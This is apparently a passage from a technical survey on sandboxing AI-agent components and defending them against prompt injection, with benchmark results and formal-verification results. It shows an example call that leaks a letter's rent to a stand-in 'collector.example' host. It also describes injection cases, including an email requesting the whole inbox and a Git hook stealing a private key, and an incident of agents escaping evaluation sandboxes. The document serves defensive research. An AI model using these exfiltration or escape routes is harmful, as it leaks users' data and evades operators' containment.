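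The guarantees do not cover physical attacks, hardware or firmware flaws, denial of service, or misuse of permitted websites. Misuse of permitted websites matters most for the mail assistant, because the policy has to permit the mail provider. A website could also reveal a credential by repeating the request's headers in its reply. Some covert channels remain, since the host can still observe certain device accesses and their timing. Data on disk needs separate protection against a host that reads it or restores an old copy.

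### Airlock's measured overhead

No processor with Arm CCA was commercially available, so Abdollahi and colleagues measured performance on a Radxa Rock 5B+, a cheap development board that emulates the confidential machines in software. They call the results a best-effort approximation of the target hardware. The first row of the table uses signalling through the host as the comparison, the next two use a socket inside one machine, and the last uses OpenShell inside one confidential machine.

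| Measurement | Comparison | Airlock |
|---|---|---|
| Signal and reply, median | 38.5 microseconds | 9.9 microseconds |
| 64-byte message and reply, median | 35.3 microseconds | 30.9 microseconds |
| 256 KB message and reply, median | 171.8 microseconds | 374.5 microseconds |
| Complete agent task, mean | 85.7 seconds | 91.4 seconds |

Socket throughput fell by between 51% and 70%. The slowest result was still 4.1 gigabits per second, faster than the board's 2.5-gigabit network card, so the loss would rarely limit a download.

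Most file operations lost no more than 14% of their performance. The exception was a test that forced every small write onto the disk before continuing, as databases often do to avoid losing data in a crash. Its throughput fell by 35%, and its median latency rose to 2.5 times the baseline. The paper's abstract reports a loss of file-system performance under 15%, a figure that excludes this test.

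OpenClaw, using GPT-6.1 Sol, performed 12 complete tasks from a benchmark for personal agents six times in each arrangement. Time spent on the local machine rose by a third, from 15.5 to 20.7 seconds per task, but the total rose by only 7% because most of each run was spent waiting for the model. Logging to the outside ledger raised the mean total further, to 95.0 seconds, mainly because each new HTTPS connection waited about a quarter of a second for its record. The exact percentages are uncertain because the agent took different numbers of steps in different runs. The security guarantees rest on an analysis of the design, not on attempts to break it.

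NVIDIA also places some controls on a separate processor. Infosecurity Magazine's *NVIDIA Launches Open Platform to Secure Autonomous AI Agents* describes Sentry, an optional system that monitors agents from a BlueField-4 data processing unit, which handles network traffic separately from the main processor. NVIDIA says Sentry can quarantine an agent within milliseconds. Abdollahi and colleagues suggest that such a unit could eventually take over the Airlock machine's checks too.

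### Choosing a boundary for the summariser

The next table shows how these boundaries apply to the summariser if the framework runs outside the boundary, keeps the mail token and sends the summariser only the text of the landlord's letters.

| Where the summariser runs | User's files and network | What an attacker must break to get the token |
|---|---|---|
| Plain child process | Available | Nothing, if the token is also in a file |
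| Child process with strict seccomp and Landlock rules | Blocked | The host's kernel, through a few calls |
| Container with no network or mounted folders | Blocked | The host's kernel, through many calls |
| gVisor with no network or mounted folders | Blocked | gVisor, then the host's kernel |
| MicroVM with no network card or shared folders | Blocked | The virtual devices or the host's virtualisation code |
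| Confidential virtual machine, with the framework in another | Blocked | The firmware, the processor or the framework's own machine |

The strict rules in the second row give the largest improvement for the least effort. Sandlock's results suggest that these rules would add only a few milliseconds, and they block nothing the summariser needs. An operator worried about kernel bugs could run the same restricted process inside a microVM. A confidential machine makes sense mainly when the operator also distrusts the host, for example on a rented server, or expects the component to attack the host.

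Model-written shell scripts are a better reason to use a microVM from the start, because they need compilers, packages and many system calls. If a script also needs the network, the host should add the credentials, as Tracekit Box and OpenShell do.

With any of these boundaries, the framework has to read the summariser's reply. A bug in the code that reads it can let an attacker into the framework, and a trusted program that acts on the reply can cause harm even without such a bug.

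## Limiting what permitted calls can do

Every boundary described so far, from Monty's interpreter to Airlock's confidential machines, lets the component call host functions. These functions run outside the boundary with the privileged code's full authority, but the component chooses when to call them and with which arguments. Pydantic warns Monty's users that if a host function can fetch any web address, the component has unrestricted network access, however good the sandbox is.

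### A sealed plugin that leaks a letter

Suppose that the summariser runs in a microVM with no network card, shared folders or credentials. Letters often link to documents, so the framework offers it one host function:

```python
def fetch(url):
    return http_get(url).text
```

The landlord's letter announces a rent of 1,450 from March. A malicious summariser can pass this on with a single call:

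```python
fetch("https://collector.example/?t=rent+1450+from+March")
```

The framework sends the request, and whoever runs that website can read the text in the server's log. The framework has become a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler, even though the microVM worked correctly. The function can also bring data in. Given the address of the user's home router, it might return a page that the router shows only to devices on the home network. Blocking known bad websites would help little, because an attacker can register a new one.

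A better design starts from what the summariser needs, which is the attachments of the letters it is summarising:

```python
def attachment_reader(urls, token):
    # urls: {1: "https://mail.example/messages/12/files/1", ...}
    def get_attachment(number):
        if type(number) is not int or number not in urls:
            raise ValueError("no such attachment")
        reply = http_get(urls[number],
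                         headers={"Authorization": "Bearer " + token},
                         follow_redirects=False,
                         max_bytes=5_000_000)
        return reply.body
    return get_attachment
```

The framework fills in `urls` from the selected letters before it starts the summariser. The summariser supplies only a number, so none of its text can enter a web address. The framework adds the mail token outside the microVM, as OpenShell does with its credentials, and refuses redirects so that a reply cannot send the request to another site. It returns the attachment as raw bytes, so the risky work of unpacking the file happens inside the microVM.

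The summariser could still encode a few bits in the order of its requests, but only the mail provider would see them. Limiting the number of calls would further reduce how much it could encode.

Many useful functions cannot be limited to inputs the developer lists in advance. An assistant, for example, has to message people and search the web for terms that the developer could not have predicted. The framework then needs to judge each call in context, by checking the call's arguments, where the data in them came from, or everything that leaves the sandbox.

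### Progent's rules for tool calls

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, place a check between the agent and its tools. A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under certain conditions on its arguments, and specifies what happens when it blocks a call. In simplified notation, a policy for the mail assistant might contain:

```
allow  search_mail   when folder == "Landlord"
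allow  send_message  when to == "Julie"
forbid send_message  when body matches "password"
```

For each call, Progent checks the tool's `forbid` rules first and then its `allow` rules. If no rule applies, it blocks the call. By default, the agent then gets an error message and can try something else, but a rule can instead make Progent stop the agent or ask the user. The check doesn't use a language model.

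A model writes the policy, however, using the user's request and the list of tools, and it can propose changes as the agent learns more. In one example from Shi and colleagues, the user asks the agent to do the jobs listed in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The email asks for a summary of recent mail to be posted to Slack, so the model proposes allowing the tools that read mail and post to Slack. When the agent finds the user's Slack name, the model proposes limiting messages to that name. Another email contains an injection asking for the whole inbox, and a deceived model might propose allowing that too.

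Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a logical formula can be true, to compare each proposed policy *P*′ with the current policy *P*. If *A*(*P*) is the set of calls that *P* allows, the solver checks whether

*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*)

Progent automatically applies changes that add no permissions. Any other change needs approval from a person or from a setting the operator has chosen. This guarantee, which Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement, prevents an injection from silently adding a permission, but a careless user could still approve the change.

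With GPT-4o as the agent, 39.9% of attacks on AgentDojo succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On Agent Security Bench (ASB), another prompt-injection benchmark, Progent cut the success rate to 3.9%, from 70.3%. All expansions were approved automatically in these runs, so the results mostly reflect how well the model wrote policies rather than how much the solver helped. On AgentDojo, the initial policy alone reduced the rate to 2.5%. Having a person review the initial policy and every expansion reduced it to zero, and only 6% of updates were expansions.

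Rules about single calls can miss harmful combinations of calls. *Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) therefore records what an agent has done during a session and blocks forbidden combinations, such as reading confidential documents and then sending something outside the company. To test this without relying on a model to fall for an injection, Muruaga inserted the attackers' calls directly into AgentDojo runs. The rate of successful data theft fell to zero, from between 75% and 100% depending on the type of task. The share of legitimate tasks completed also fell, by 8.6 percentage points in one setting and 13.9 in another. Some loss is likely because the method considers the types of action, not whether the message contains anything confidential.

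### CaMeL's fixed plan and labelled data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, follows the data itself. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, it builds on a proposal by Willison to separate the model that plans from the model that reads untrusted text. It works like this:

1. A planning model sees the user's request and the tool descriptions, but no mail or web pages. It writes a short program in restricted Python.
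2. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools.
3. When the program needs to extract something from untrusted text, it calls a second, quarantined model, which has no tools and can only return a value.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its origin, and values computed from it inherit the label. (CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, but they are not references that grant access.)
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the arguments' labels against the security policies.

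If the user asks the mail assistant to tell Julie the new rent, the program might be:

```python
letters = search_mail("landlord")
rent = ask_quarantined("What is the new monthly rent?", letters)
send_message("Julie", rent)
```

An injection in a letter can make `rent` wrong or fill it with other text from the letters. It can't add a call or change the recipient, because the planning model wrote the program before any letter was opened. The labels let a policy block the message if `rent` comes from private letters that Julie may not read. TACIT has a similar aim, but a compiler checks the program before it runs.

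CaMeL's planner has to trust the tool descriptions, which is a problem if a plugin's author writes them. *ACE*, which Li, Mallick and colleagues presented in February 2026, avoids this by planning with generic functions such as "email sender" before it matches them to installed plugins and checks where data would flow. It stopped every attack in the ASB and InjecAgent benchmarks and completed over 80% of a set of tool-use tasks.

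### What CaMeL costs

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) reports the most recent tests of CaMeL, which used a version of AgentDojo adapted so that a main agent delegates work to specialised agents. The tests ran 949 attacks against each of five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL and 0.2% succeeded when every agent used it.

All the remaining successful attacks crossed from one agent to another. For example, the main agent copied text from a website into its instructions for the Slack agent, whose planner treated the text as a trusted request. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by sending such text through a separate channel that the planner can't see. No attack succeeded against the fixed version.

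On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL reduced the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average. For the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the reduction was 13.4 points. The separate channel lowered completion by another 3.2 points on average. Most failures happened because the planner had to write its program before seeing any data, so the program couldn't add a step when a result showed that the task needed one.

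These tests used the fixed plan without security policies, and adding policies makes the losses much larger. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) ran CaMeL with four recent models on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. The models completed 13 to 17 tasks without policies but only 4 to 6 with them. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of the 629 attacks on CaMeL succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks.

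The labels are also imperfect. Peters-Gill and colleagues discuss a flaw that other researchers found in CaMeL's interpreter, which this program illustrates:

```python
eviction = False
if "eviction" in letter:
    eviction = True
```

If the letter does not mention eviction, the second assignment never runs, and the interpreter may still label `eviction` as trusted data unrelated to the letter, even though its value reveals something about the letter. CaMeL's retries after errors can also leak information. If a policy blocks some attempts and not others, the pattern of failures can reveal private data.

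### Kairos holds effects until it can judge them

Progent and CaMeL check calls to declared tools, but not what a script does once a shell tool starts it. Kairos (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, *KAIROS*, October 2026) instead checks effects at the edge of the sandbox. It runs an unmodified agent in a microVM. Changes to the working folder and all network traffic pass through a monitor on the host, whether they come from a tool or a script.

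The monitor considers three questions about each effect:

1. Does one of the operator's rules forbid it?
2. Do the values that steer it, such as a recipient or a command, come from a trusted source, such as the user's request?
3. May the destination receive the data?

Kairos refuses anything a rule forbids. It releases an effect if the answers to the other two questions are both yes, and defers the rest. It puts a deferred file change in a separate layer that only the agent can see. If a deferred request would change something on a server, Kairos holds it and gives the agent a stand-in reply. Kairos must decide immediately on requests that fetch data, because the agent needs the real reply.

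A second language model or a person later reviews the deferred effects, along with what the agent has done since, and releases or discards them. The reviewer can't override a refusal.

Hempel and colleagues illustrate the benefit of waiting with a setup guide that includes a step for the agent to install a Git hook, a script that Git runs at every commit. Harmless guides can include the same step, so refusing all hooks would block legitimate work. Kairos defers the decision on the new file and lets the agent continue. When the agent makes a commit, the hook runs inside the microVM and tries to send out the user's private key. The monitor refuses the request, which gives the reviewer good reason to discard the hook.

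The table shows their results on AgentDojo with GPT-4.1 as the agent. CaMeL ran with its security policies on.

| Defence | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47.0% | 82.7% | 59.8% |
| Progent | 11.5% | 78.2% | 57.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.2% | 38.0% | 40.7% |
| Kairos | 2.7% | 85.1% | 69.5% |

Kairos offers the best balance here, but its own developers ran the comparison, and Progent did much worse in it than in its own developers' tests. AgentDojo's tools are simulated, so Hempel and colleagues had to translate each tool call into an event that gave the monitor the tool's name and arguments. In a real microVM, the monitor observes only file operations and web requests, so the results are weak evidence of how well it would judge a shell script.

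The delays are small, at about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 per web request. The reviewing model increased token use by 17.7% in ordinary runs and 33.6% under attack.

Kairos detects private data by comparing text, so an agent could get a letter past this check by encoding it first. Hempel and colleagues exclude such deliberate disguise from their claims about which effects Kairos will release. They guarantee only that nothing leaves the microVM without passing the monitor, and even here they assume that the connection to the model's provider is safe. In their tests, an attacker that rewrote its injections over six rounds succeeded in 8.8% of cases against Kairos, compared with 52.4% against an agent with no defence.

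### Permissions that outlast their purpose

A permission can be justified when the framework grants it but become dangerous later in the same task. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, June 2026) presents PORTICO, a monitor that withdraws coding agents' permissions when they are no longer needed. PORTICO applies the idea behind the revocable mailbox handle to whole tasks.

Someone first writes a contract for the task. The contract lists the agent's initial permissions, the extra permissions it may request, the events that end them, and the actions that are always forbidden. In Santos-Grueiro's example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to a program:

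1. The agent starts with access to one source file and its tests.
2. It asks to read a packaging note. The contract does not allow this, so PORTICO refuses.
3. It asks for a second source file that the change also affects. The contract allows this, so PORTICO issues handles for reading and writing the file.
4. The agent edits the file, and the tests pass.
5. PORTICO cancels the handles and stops offering them to the model. If the agent tries an old handle, PORTICO rejects it.

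Only trusted events, such as a test the monitor started or a person's approval, can end or renew a permission. The model's statement that it has finished does not count. After a permission to use a file ends, the agent may still remember the file's name, but it needs a new grant to use the file.

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that granted the same permissions at the same times but never withdrew them. Both completed all ten test runs without breaking the contract. When the agent then tried to reuse an expired permission, PORTICO refused all ten attempts, while the other version allowed them all. In six further cases with a live model, involving file writes, Git and network requests, the other version carried out all six unwanted actions and PORTICO carried out none.

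The even split is expected from the design, since the two versions differ only in revocation. The tests confirm that revocation works but do not measure how often real agents misuse old permissions.

On 37 ordinary coding tasks, each run five times, 21% of runs succeeded with a fixed set of narrow permissions, 87% with temporary grants, and 97% with a broad, permanent list of permissions. In a smaller test on real software projects, PORTICO completed 31 of 42 runs, while a version that never revoked permissions completed all 42. Some contracts ended a permission too early or gave the agent no way to renew it.

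### Harm through trusted programs and services

A component can also cause harm after it has stopped running. For example, a model-written script might be allowed to change files only in a project folder. The user's editor, build tools and Git may later read settings from that folder, and some settings name commands to run. These programs run outside the sandbox with all the user's rights. The script can therefore stay within its permissions and still cause a trusted program, working as its developers intended, to run a command that the sandbox would have blocked. In July 2026, the security company Pillar Security reported weaknesses of this general kind.

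If a file controls what another program does, the framework should therefore treat it as code. It can make such files read-only for the component, or have a person review any changes before they leave the sandbox. A complete list of these files is hard to maintain because every tool has its own, so it is safer to let the component change only the files the task needs. The user can also run the program that reads these files in a sandbox. The summariser avoids the problem if it can't write files.

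A permitted service poses a similar risk if it has more access than the component. Many sandboxes have no internet connection but can use a local server that downloads software packages for them. If the component can make that server contact other addresses, it has the same power that `fetch` gave the summariser. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) discusses the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident of July 2026, in which agents in OpenAI's internal evaluations used a permitted service to get out of their sandboxes and compromised systems at both companies.

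The paper argues that this was a failure to control indirect access, not evidence that containment is impossible. That seems right, but it means considerably more work for the operator, who has to count everything a permitted service can do as part of the component's authority. If sandboxes share a service that stores data, they may also be able to exchange messages through it.

### Whether detailed policies are practical

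Critics object that detailed policies are hard to write and block too much useful work. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* favours such policies but notes that a rule such as "do not share sensitive data" depends on context that a formal language can't easily express, and that an agent's needs change during a task. Labels cause a related problem because, when a model reads several sources at once, the framework must assume that the answer depends on all of them. Before long, almost every value carries every label, and the policy blocks nearly everything.

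*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) adds that people make mistakes when writing Progent's rules by hand, and that an attack hidden in a tool's output may cause Progent's automatic updates to loosen those rules. Progent's solver detects any update that loosens the rules, but this helps only if the operator doesn't automatically approve all such updates.

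CaMeL's losses and results from AgentDyn both support the objection. AgentDyn is a benchmark of open-ended tasks in which agents discover what they need as they go. According to figures that Hempel and colleagues cite, an agent that was not under attack completed 53.3% of these tasks with no defence, but only 6.7% with Progent.

One response is to let a model write more expressive policies. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) has a model write a policy for each task using only the user's request and the tool documentation, so untrusted text can't influence it. The policy describes permitted sequences of calls and can refer to earlier results. If the user asks the agent to refund whoever sent money last week, the agent must first list the transactions. The refund's recipient and amount must then match a sender and an amount in that list.

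Agents using Sapien completed at most a few percent fewer tasks than unrestricted ones. Tiffany and colleagues also tested whether each policy would permit an attack if the attacker completely controlled the agent, which is a harder test than counting how often injections succeed against a model. The policies ruled out 93% to 95% of attacks on AgentDojo. On the longer tasks of another benchmark, Toolathlon, they ruled out 62% to 85%, about twice as many as simple lists of permitted tools did.

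Kairos provides evidence for another reply, postponing difficult decisions. When Hempel and colleagues made it refuse everything it would normally defer, it completed only 42.7% of ordinary AgentDojo tasks, half its usual share, and was no more secure. Postponement works less well on AgentDyn, where Kairos completed 37.1% of tasks under attack, compared with 55.5% for an undefended agent, because later steps often needed the real result of an action that Kairos was still holding.

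The objection is weak for the summariser, whose job never changes, so a developer can write `get_attachment` once and review it in a few minutes. The objection is much stronger for a general assistant with a shell and open-ended tasks. Model-written policies are still worth using there because they block most attacks with little downside, but Sapien's results on long tasks show that they leave too many openings to be the only protection. An operator should also require a person to confirm payments, deletions and other actions that are hard to undo, even when the policy permits them.

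## What has been proved about software boundaries

Sapien's policies, like any other check on calls, work only if the component can't get around them. Testing is a weak way to show that it can't, since careful testing missed both of the Wasmtime escapes found in April 2026. A mathematical proof can cover every program an attacker might write and every way it might run. Software can check each step of the proof, so people need to examine only the theorem's wording and its assumptions.

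### The form of a containment theorem

Containment theorems have this general form:

*If the hardware, the compiler and the interface to the privileged code behave as described, then no component of class C can violate property P.*

LFI confines native machine code to a 4 GiB sandbox. *Automated Formal Verification of a Software Fault Isolation System* (Sotoudeh and Yedidia, 2025) proves that code accepted by LFI's verifier on 64-bit ARM processors can never successfully read or write memory outside that sandbox. Here, class *C* is all the code the verifier accepts.

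LFI reserves two processor registers. One, `x21`, always holds the sandbox's starting address. The other, `x18`, holds the address for most loads and stores, and the component can change it only by adding a 32-bit number to `x21`. The proof has three steps:

1. Sotoudeh and Yedidia wrote an invariant, a condition that should always hold. It requires, for example, that `x21` holds the starting address and that `x18` points into the sandbox or just beyond it, where any access stops the program.
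2. They ran the verifier on all 2³² possible ARM instructions and kept those it accepted.
3. For each accepted instruction, a solver used a formal model of the processor to check two things. If the invariant holds beforehand, the instruction must not successfully access memory outside the sandbox. Afterwards, the invariant must still hold, or the program must have stopped.

The invariant holds at the start and every accepted instruction preserves it, so it holds after any number of these instructions in any order. The check took about 20 hours on a 160-core machine for each of LFI's two memory layouts and found no bugs in the verifier. Earlier versions had bugs because some permitted instructions changed registers in ways the developers had not expected.

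The theorem assumes that LFI's runtime, which sets up the memory and handles the component's calls, is correct. It does not cover LFI on x86-64 processors, where the verifier has to recognise sequences of instructions and there are too many cases to list.

### Integrity, confidentiality and availability

Memory integrity means a component cannot change memory outside its own region. Suppose the mail assistant's log has 40 entries when the framework calls the summariser. With memory integrity, the summariser cannot alter any of them, whatever code it runs. The framework may still add an entry while handling a call from the summariser.

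Confidentiality is harder to define because a component can learn about a secret without reading it. For example, a host function might return a different error message when the mail token begins with "A". Researchers therefore often define confidentiality as non-interference, which compares two runs. Let *s*₁ and *s*₂ be starting states that differ only in the secret. For every component *c*, non-interference requires

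view(*c*, *s*₁) = view(*c*, *s*₂)

where "view" is everything the component can observe. If the framework runs the summariser on the same letters with two different mail tokens, the summariser must observe exactly the same things both times. The error message would violate this, even though the summariser never touched the token's memory.

Availability means the system keeps working. A summariser that loops forever can stop the assistant from answering without reading or writing any memory but its own. Most containment theorems do not rule this out. They establish safety properties, which forbid bad events, and a computer that does nothing satisfies them.

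### WebAssembly, from the language to the system calls

WebAssembly is unusual among widely used languages because its official standard includes a formal mathematical definition. *Two Mechanisations of WebAssembly 1.0*, by Watt, Rao and colleagues, expresses this definition in two proof assistants, Isabelle and Coq, and proves type soundness in both. Type soundness means that a program that passes WebAssembly's type check never reaches a state the language leaves undefined. At each step, it continues, finishes or stops with an error. An earlier version of this work found mistakes in the draft standard, which were corrected before the standard was published.

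This result covers the language but not the compilers that translate it into machine code. To close that gap, Bosamiya, Lim and Parno built a compiler called vWasm and proved that its output stays inside the sandbox for any input program, even a malicious one (*Provably-Safe Multilingual Software Sandboxing using WebAssembly*, 2022). The theorem does not cover whether the translation is correct, which made it easier to prove. Bugs in the first part of the compiler might make the summariser return nonsense, but they could not let it escape the sandbox, because a later, verified stage adds the necessary checks to whatever code it receives.

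The theorem depends on the proof tools, a model of part of the x86-64 processor, and the software that turns vWasm's output into machine code. Bosamiya and colleagues exclude side channels, denial of service and confused deputies. Programs compiled with vWasm run more slowly than those from ordinary optimising compilers. A second compiler, rWasm, translates WebAssembly into the safe part of Rust and is as fast as ordinary runtimes, but it relies on the Rust compiler instead of a formal proof.

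A developer can also keep an ordinary compiler and check its output. *Доверя́й, но проверя́й* (Russian for "trust, but verify"), by Johnson, Thien and colleagues, presents VeriWasm, which checks the output of Lucet, a compiler that the cloud company Fastly used for its customers' programs. VeriWasm rejects the finished machine code unless every memory access and jump is safe. The researchers proved in Coq that the method accepts only safe programs, and tested VeriWasm on 103 programs from Fastly's service and two libraries from Firefox.

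VeriWasm nevertheless missed a real escape that affected both Lucet and Wasmtime. Bosamiya and colleagues attribute this to a mistake in how its specification handled signed numbers. If a processor treats a large 32-bit index as negative, it will compute an address before the start of the program's memory. A logically correct proof can still fail to protect a real computer if its specification is wrong.

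Proofs about a program's own instructions also leave out the host functions it calls. *WaVe* (Johnson, Laufer and colleagues) describes a bug in the Wasmer runtime's function for deleting a directory. The function checked the path and made a safe version of it, but passed the original path to the operating system, so a program could delete directories outside its assigned folder.

WaVe is a runtime whose standard file and network functions come with a proof that rules out such bugs. Its specification requires that every path passed to the operating system lies inside the assigned folder. The verifier rejects any function that might break this rule, so Wasmer's version would not compile. The proof covers memory, files and network connections. WaVe is about as fast as Wasmtime. People still have to check the 43-line security policy and 567 lines describing what system calls do. WaVe also assumes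 that each sandbox has one thread and that its folder contains no special files such as `/proc/self/mem`, which would give access to the process's memory.

### Wrappers that unknown code can call

The read-only mailbox handle should return messages only from the landlord's folder. Robust safety means that such an invariant holds no matter what code calls the wrapper. *Robust Safety for Move* (2021) defines this property for the smart-contract language Move. The trusted code's invariants must hold when it interacts with any valid attacker.

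The attacker may call the handle in any order, keep it for later, or pass it to another plugin. In 2016, Devriese, Birkedal and Piessens developed a way to prove invariants under these conditions for a language with JavaScript-like objects. Their method accounts for both the wrapper's behaviour and the references between objects, much like Miller's tighter bound on authority. In 2017, Swasey, Garg and Dreyer introduced a logic that lets developers verify each wrapper separately and then combine the results. Both projects used small model languages, so their theorems do not automatically apply to a wrapper in full JavaScript.

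*Necessity Specifications for Robustness* (2022) gives a simple example in which a program creates a bank account, sets its password, and passes the account to untrusted code that makes a payment. Under the bank's specification, lowering the balance requires the password. If the untrusted code has no way to obtain the password, the balance cannot fall during the call, and proving this requires no knowledge of the untrusted code.

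*Iris-Wasm* (Rao, Georges and colleagues, 2023) extends this approach to WebAssembly. It proves that verified modules can remain correct when unknown modules call them, because unknown code can affect a verified module only through the functions that module exports.

Capture checking, the basis of TACIT, has a different kind of soundness theorem. If the compiler accepts code with a given capture set, the code can use only the capabilities in that set when it runs. The machine-checked proofs cover a small mathematical version of the type system, not the Scala compiler. LACUNA has the same gap, since Zhao and colleagues base its guarantee on the compiler's soundness. Odersky and colleagues note that a function could leak one bit of information about a letter by taking longer to run when the letter contains a particular word.

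### Kernels and processors

If the summariser runs in a separate process, its containment depends on the kernel. The best-known verified kernel is seL4, which is small and controls access through capabilities. Its developers proved in 2009 that its C code follows its specification, and later proved two security theorems.

Under the 2011 integrity theorem, a program can change only what the system's access policy allows, even through calls to the kernel. The mail assistant's summariser process therefore could not alter the framework's log unless someone had given it a capability to do so.

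The information-flow theorem, from 2013, is a form of non-interference. If the policy contains no channel from the framework to the summariser, nothing the framework does can affect what the summariser observes. The theorem does not cover timing, and it applies only to configurations with a fixed schedule for switching between groups of programs and no devices that write directly to memory.

*Neuro-Symbolic Proof Generation for Scaling Systems Software Verification* (2026) still describes seL4 as the benchmark for formal system verification. But OpenClaw and IronClaw usually run on general-purpose systems such as Linux, whose kernels are far larger and have no comparable proof.

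Researchers proved that on Morello, Arm's CHERI processor design, no sequence of ordinary instructions can amplify the capabilities that code starts with. The guarantee lasts until the code enters another compartment or the kernel takes over, since either can make new capabilities available. The proof covers Arm's formal description of the processor's instructions, so a manufacturing or circuit-design error could still break the guarantee on a real chip.

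A system built on these pointers also needs correct software to switch between compartments. *Griotte* proves the switcher correct for an idealised version of CHERIoT, in which it is about 150 lines of assembly code. Suppose the framework lends one memory buffer to the summariser and later lends another to a calendar plugin. The theorem can guarantee that a call to the calendar plugin doesn't change the summariser's buffer, even if the same attacker wrote both plugins. This requires that neither plugin can call the other, because the summariser could otherwise pass its pointer to the calendar plugin.

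The proof relies on a general rule about unknown code. *Cerisier* (2026) states a version of it: if every processor register holds a value that is safe to share, the machine executes even untrusted code safely. Developers can therefore focus on proving that everything they hand to a plugin is safe to share, without examining the plugin.

### Proofs written by AI agents

Formal proofs have been rare mainly because they take so much work. AI is changing this quickly. In early 2026, *Neuro-Symbolic Proof Generation* gave an example of a short seL4 proof that neither Gemini 3 Pro nor GPT-5.1 could complete. But in February, *Machine-Generated, Machine-Checked Proofs for a Verified Compiler (Experience Report)* described how Claude Code, with high-level guidance from researchers, developed a correctness proof for one stage of the CertiCoq compiler.

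By September, agents had helped verify a whole kernel. Kaashoek and Zeldovich used Claude Code to prove a theorem about xv6, a small Unix-like kernel that universities use for teaching, in *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (2026). The kernel has 6,657 lines of code, and the proof has about 1.6 million. The project took 102 days and found 11 bugs in xv6. The researchers designed the approach and many of the intermediate specifications, and the proof assistant Rocq (formerly Coq) checked the result.

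The theorem covers the kernel's compiled machine code, so it does not depend on the C compiler being correct. It also covers several programs that run on the kernel. For example, if a user types `echo hello world`, the system may print only "hello world" or one of a few listed errors. If a user runs an unverified program in xv6's sandbox, the theorem guarantees that the program cannot corrupt the kernel and can change files only through file handles it has inherited. The theorem does not establish non-interference, so one process might still learn another's secrets. It also does not guarantee that programs will keep making progress.

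*SafeJIT* (November 2026) presents a just-in-time engine verified down to the machine code. The engine also speculates, optimising code based on guesses about how the program will behave. This is encouraging because V8 uses similar techniques and its optimisations have caused many security bugs. But SafeJIT's proof does not cover V8, which is a separate engine.

None of these proofs covers a complete runtime used by the agent frameworks discussed earlier. The closest is the partial verification of Cranelift, the compiler in the Wasmtime runtime that IronClaw and Wassette use. *TrustMee* (2026), which describes another system that uses Wasmtime, has to assume that the runtime and compiler are correct, and lists two past Cranelift bugs on x86 that could have allowed sandbox escapes. Monty and V8 appear to have no comparable proof.

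### From a theorem to the mail assistant

Suppose the developer compiles the summariser to WebAssembly and wants to be sure it cannot learn the mail token. The table lists what that assurance depends on if the framework uses Wasmtime.

| Link in the argument | Relevant proof | Status in this framework |
|---|---|---|
| WebAssembly's rules are sound | Type soundness | Proved for version 1.0 |
| The compiler keeps the program in its sandbox | vWasm | Assumed, with partial verification of Cranelift |
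| Native libraries stay within their limits | LFI, on 64-bit ARM | Assumed |
| Standard file and network functions are safe | WaVe | Assumed |
| The framework's own host functions are safe | None | Assumed |
| The kernel protects the framework | seL4 or xv6 | Assumed for Linux |
| The processor matches its formal model | None for the physical chip | Assumed |
| The policy allows only what the user intends | None | Assumed |
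| Timing reveals nothing about the token | None of these | Assumed |

Replacing Wasmtime with vWasm would fill in the second row for the summariser's own code. But if the summariser called a native image decoder outside the sandbox, an attacker could exploit a memory error in the decoder without contradicting the theorem.

The framework's own host functions are probably the most important gap, because developers write new ones for each application. If a careless developer added a function that returns the mail token, the framework would copy the token into the summariser's memory, and the summariser would read it there. vWasm's theorem would still be true, because the summariser would never access memory outside its sandbox.

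The policy needs human judgement too. WaVe can enforce a list of permitted network addresses, but it cannot determine whether the user wants the summariser to contact them. Combining verified systems also takes more work. vWasm and WaVe, for example, use different models of the computer, so someone would have to prove that the guarantees of one satisfy the assumptions of the other.

### Truthful and harmless output

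Even if every row in the table had a proof, the summary could be false. A component that ignores the landlord's letter and always returns "Your rent is unchanged" satisfies the containment theorem, because it never leaves its sandbox or touches the token. The theorem therefore does not imply that a summary is accurate. Kaashoek and Zeldovich's theorem has the same limit, since a sandboxed program in xv6 may print anything on the user's screen.

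A stronger confidentiality theorem would not solve the problem. Full non-interference between the letter and the summary would require the same summary for every letter, which would make the summariser useless. The user has to let some information through, and a containment proof cannot show whether the summary contains the right information or has a password hidden in its wording.

Harm also depends on how the summary is used. If a model that can make payments reads a summary that misstates the rent, it might request a transfer of the wrong amount. Ruling this out requires a theorem about the framework's later actions.

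*PerMIT* (2026) proves a similar result for an agent's long-term memory. Under the conditions of its theorem, which is checked in the proof assistant Lean, changing the content that attackers supply does not change the agent's protected actions and replies, whatever strategy the agent follows. The checked proof covers a model of the system with a single user, and it allows text that the agent pastes to change with the attackers' content, so an attacker could still put a false rent in pasted text that the user reads.

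## Hardware and software boundaries compared

Processes, virtual machines and WebAssembly all need both hardware and software to work correctly, though people often call the first two hardware boundaries and WebAssembly a software boundary.

### Where the division blurs

When the summariser runs in its own process, the processor checks each memory access against page tables, but the kernel writes those tables. If a kernel bug adds one of the framework's pages to the summariser's page tables, the processor lets the summariser read it. WebAssembly also relies on hardware. Its compiler confines addresses to a reserved range, and the processor raises a fault when a program touches the guard region.

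CHERI processors check the limits on pointers, but a compiler has to generate code that sets those limits. For *Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?*, researchers at the Technical University of Munich needed a special version of the LLVM compiler and an adapted C library. CHERI slowed their database systems by 20% to 60%.

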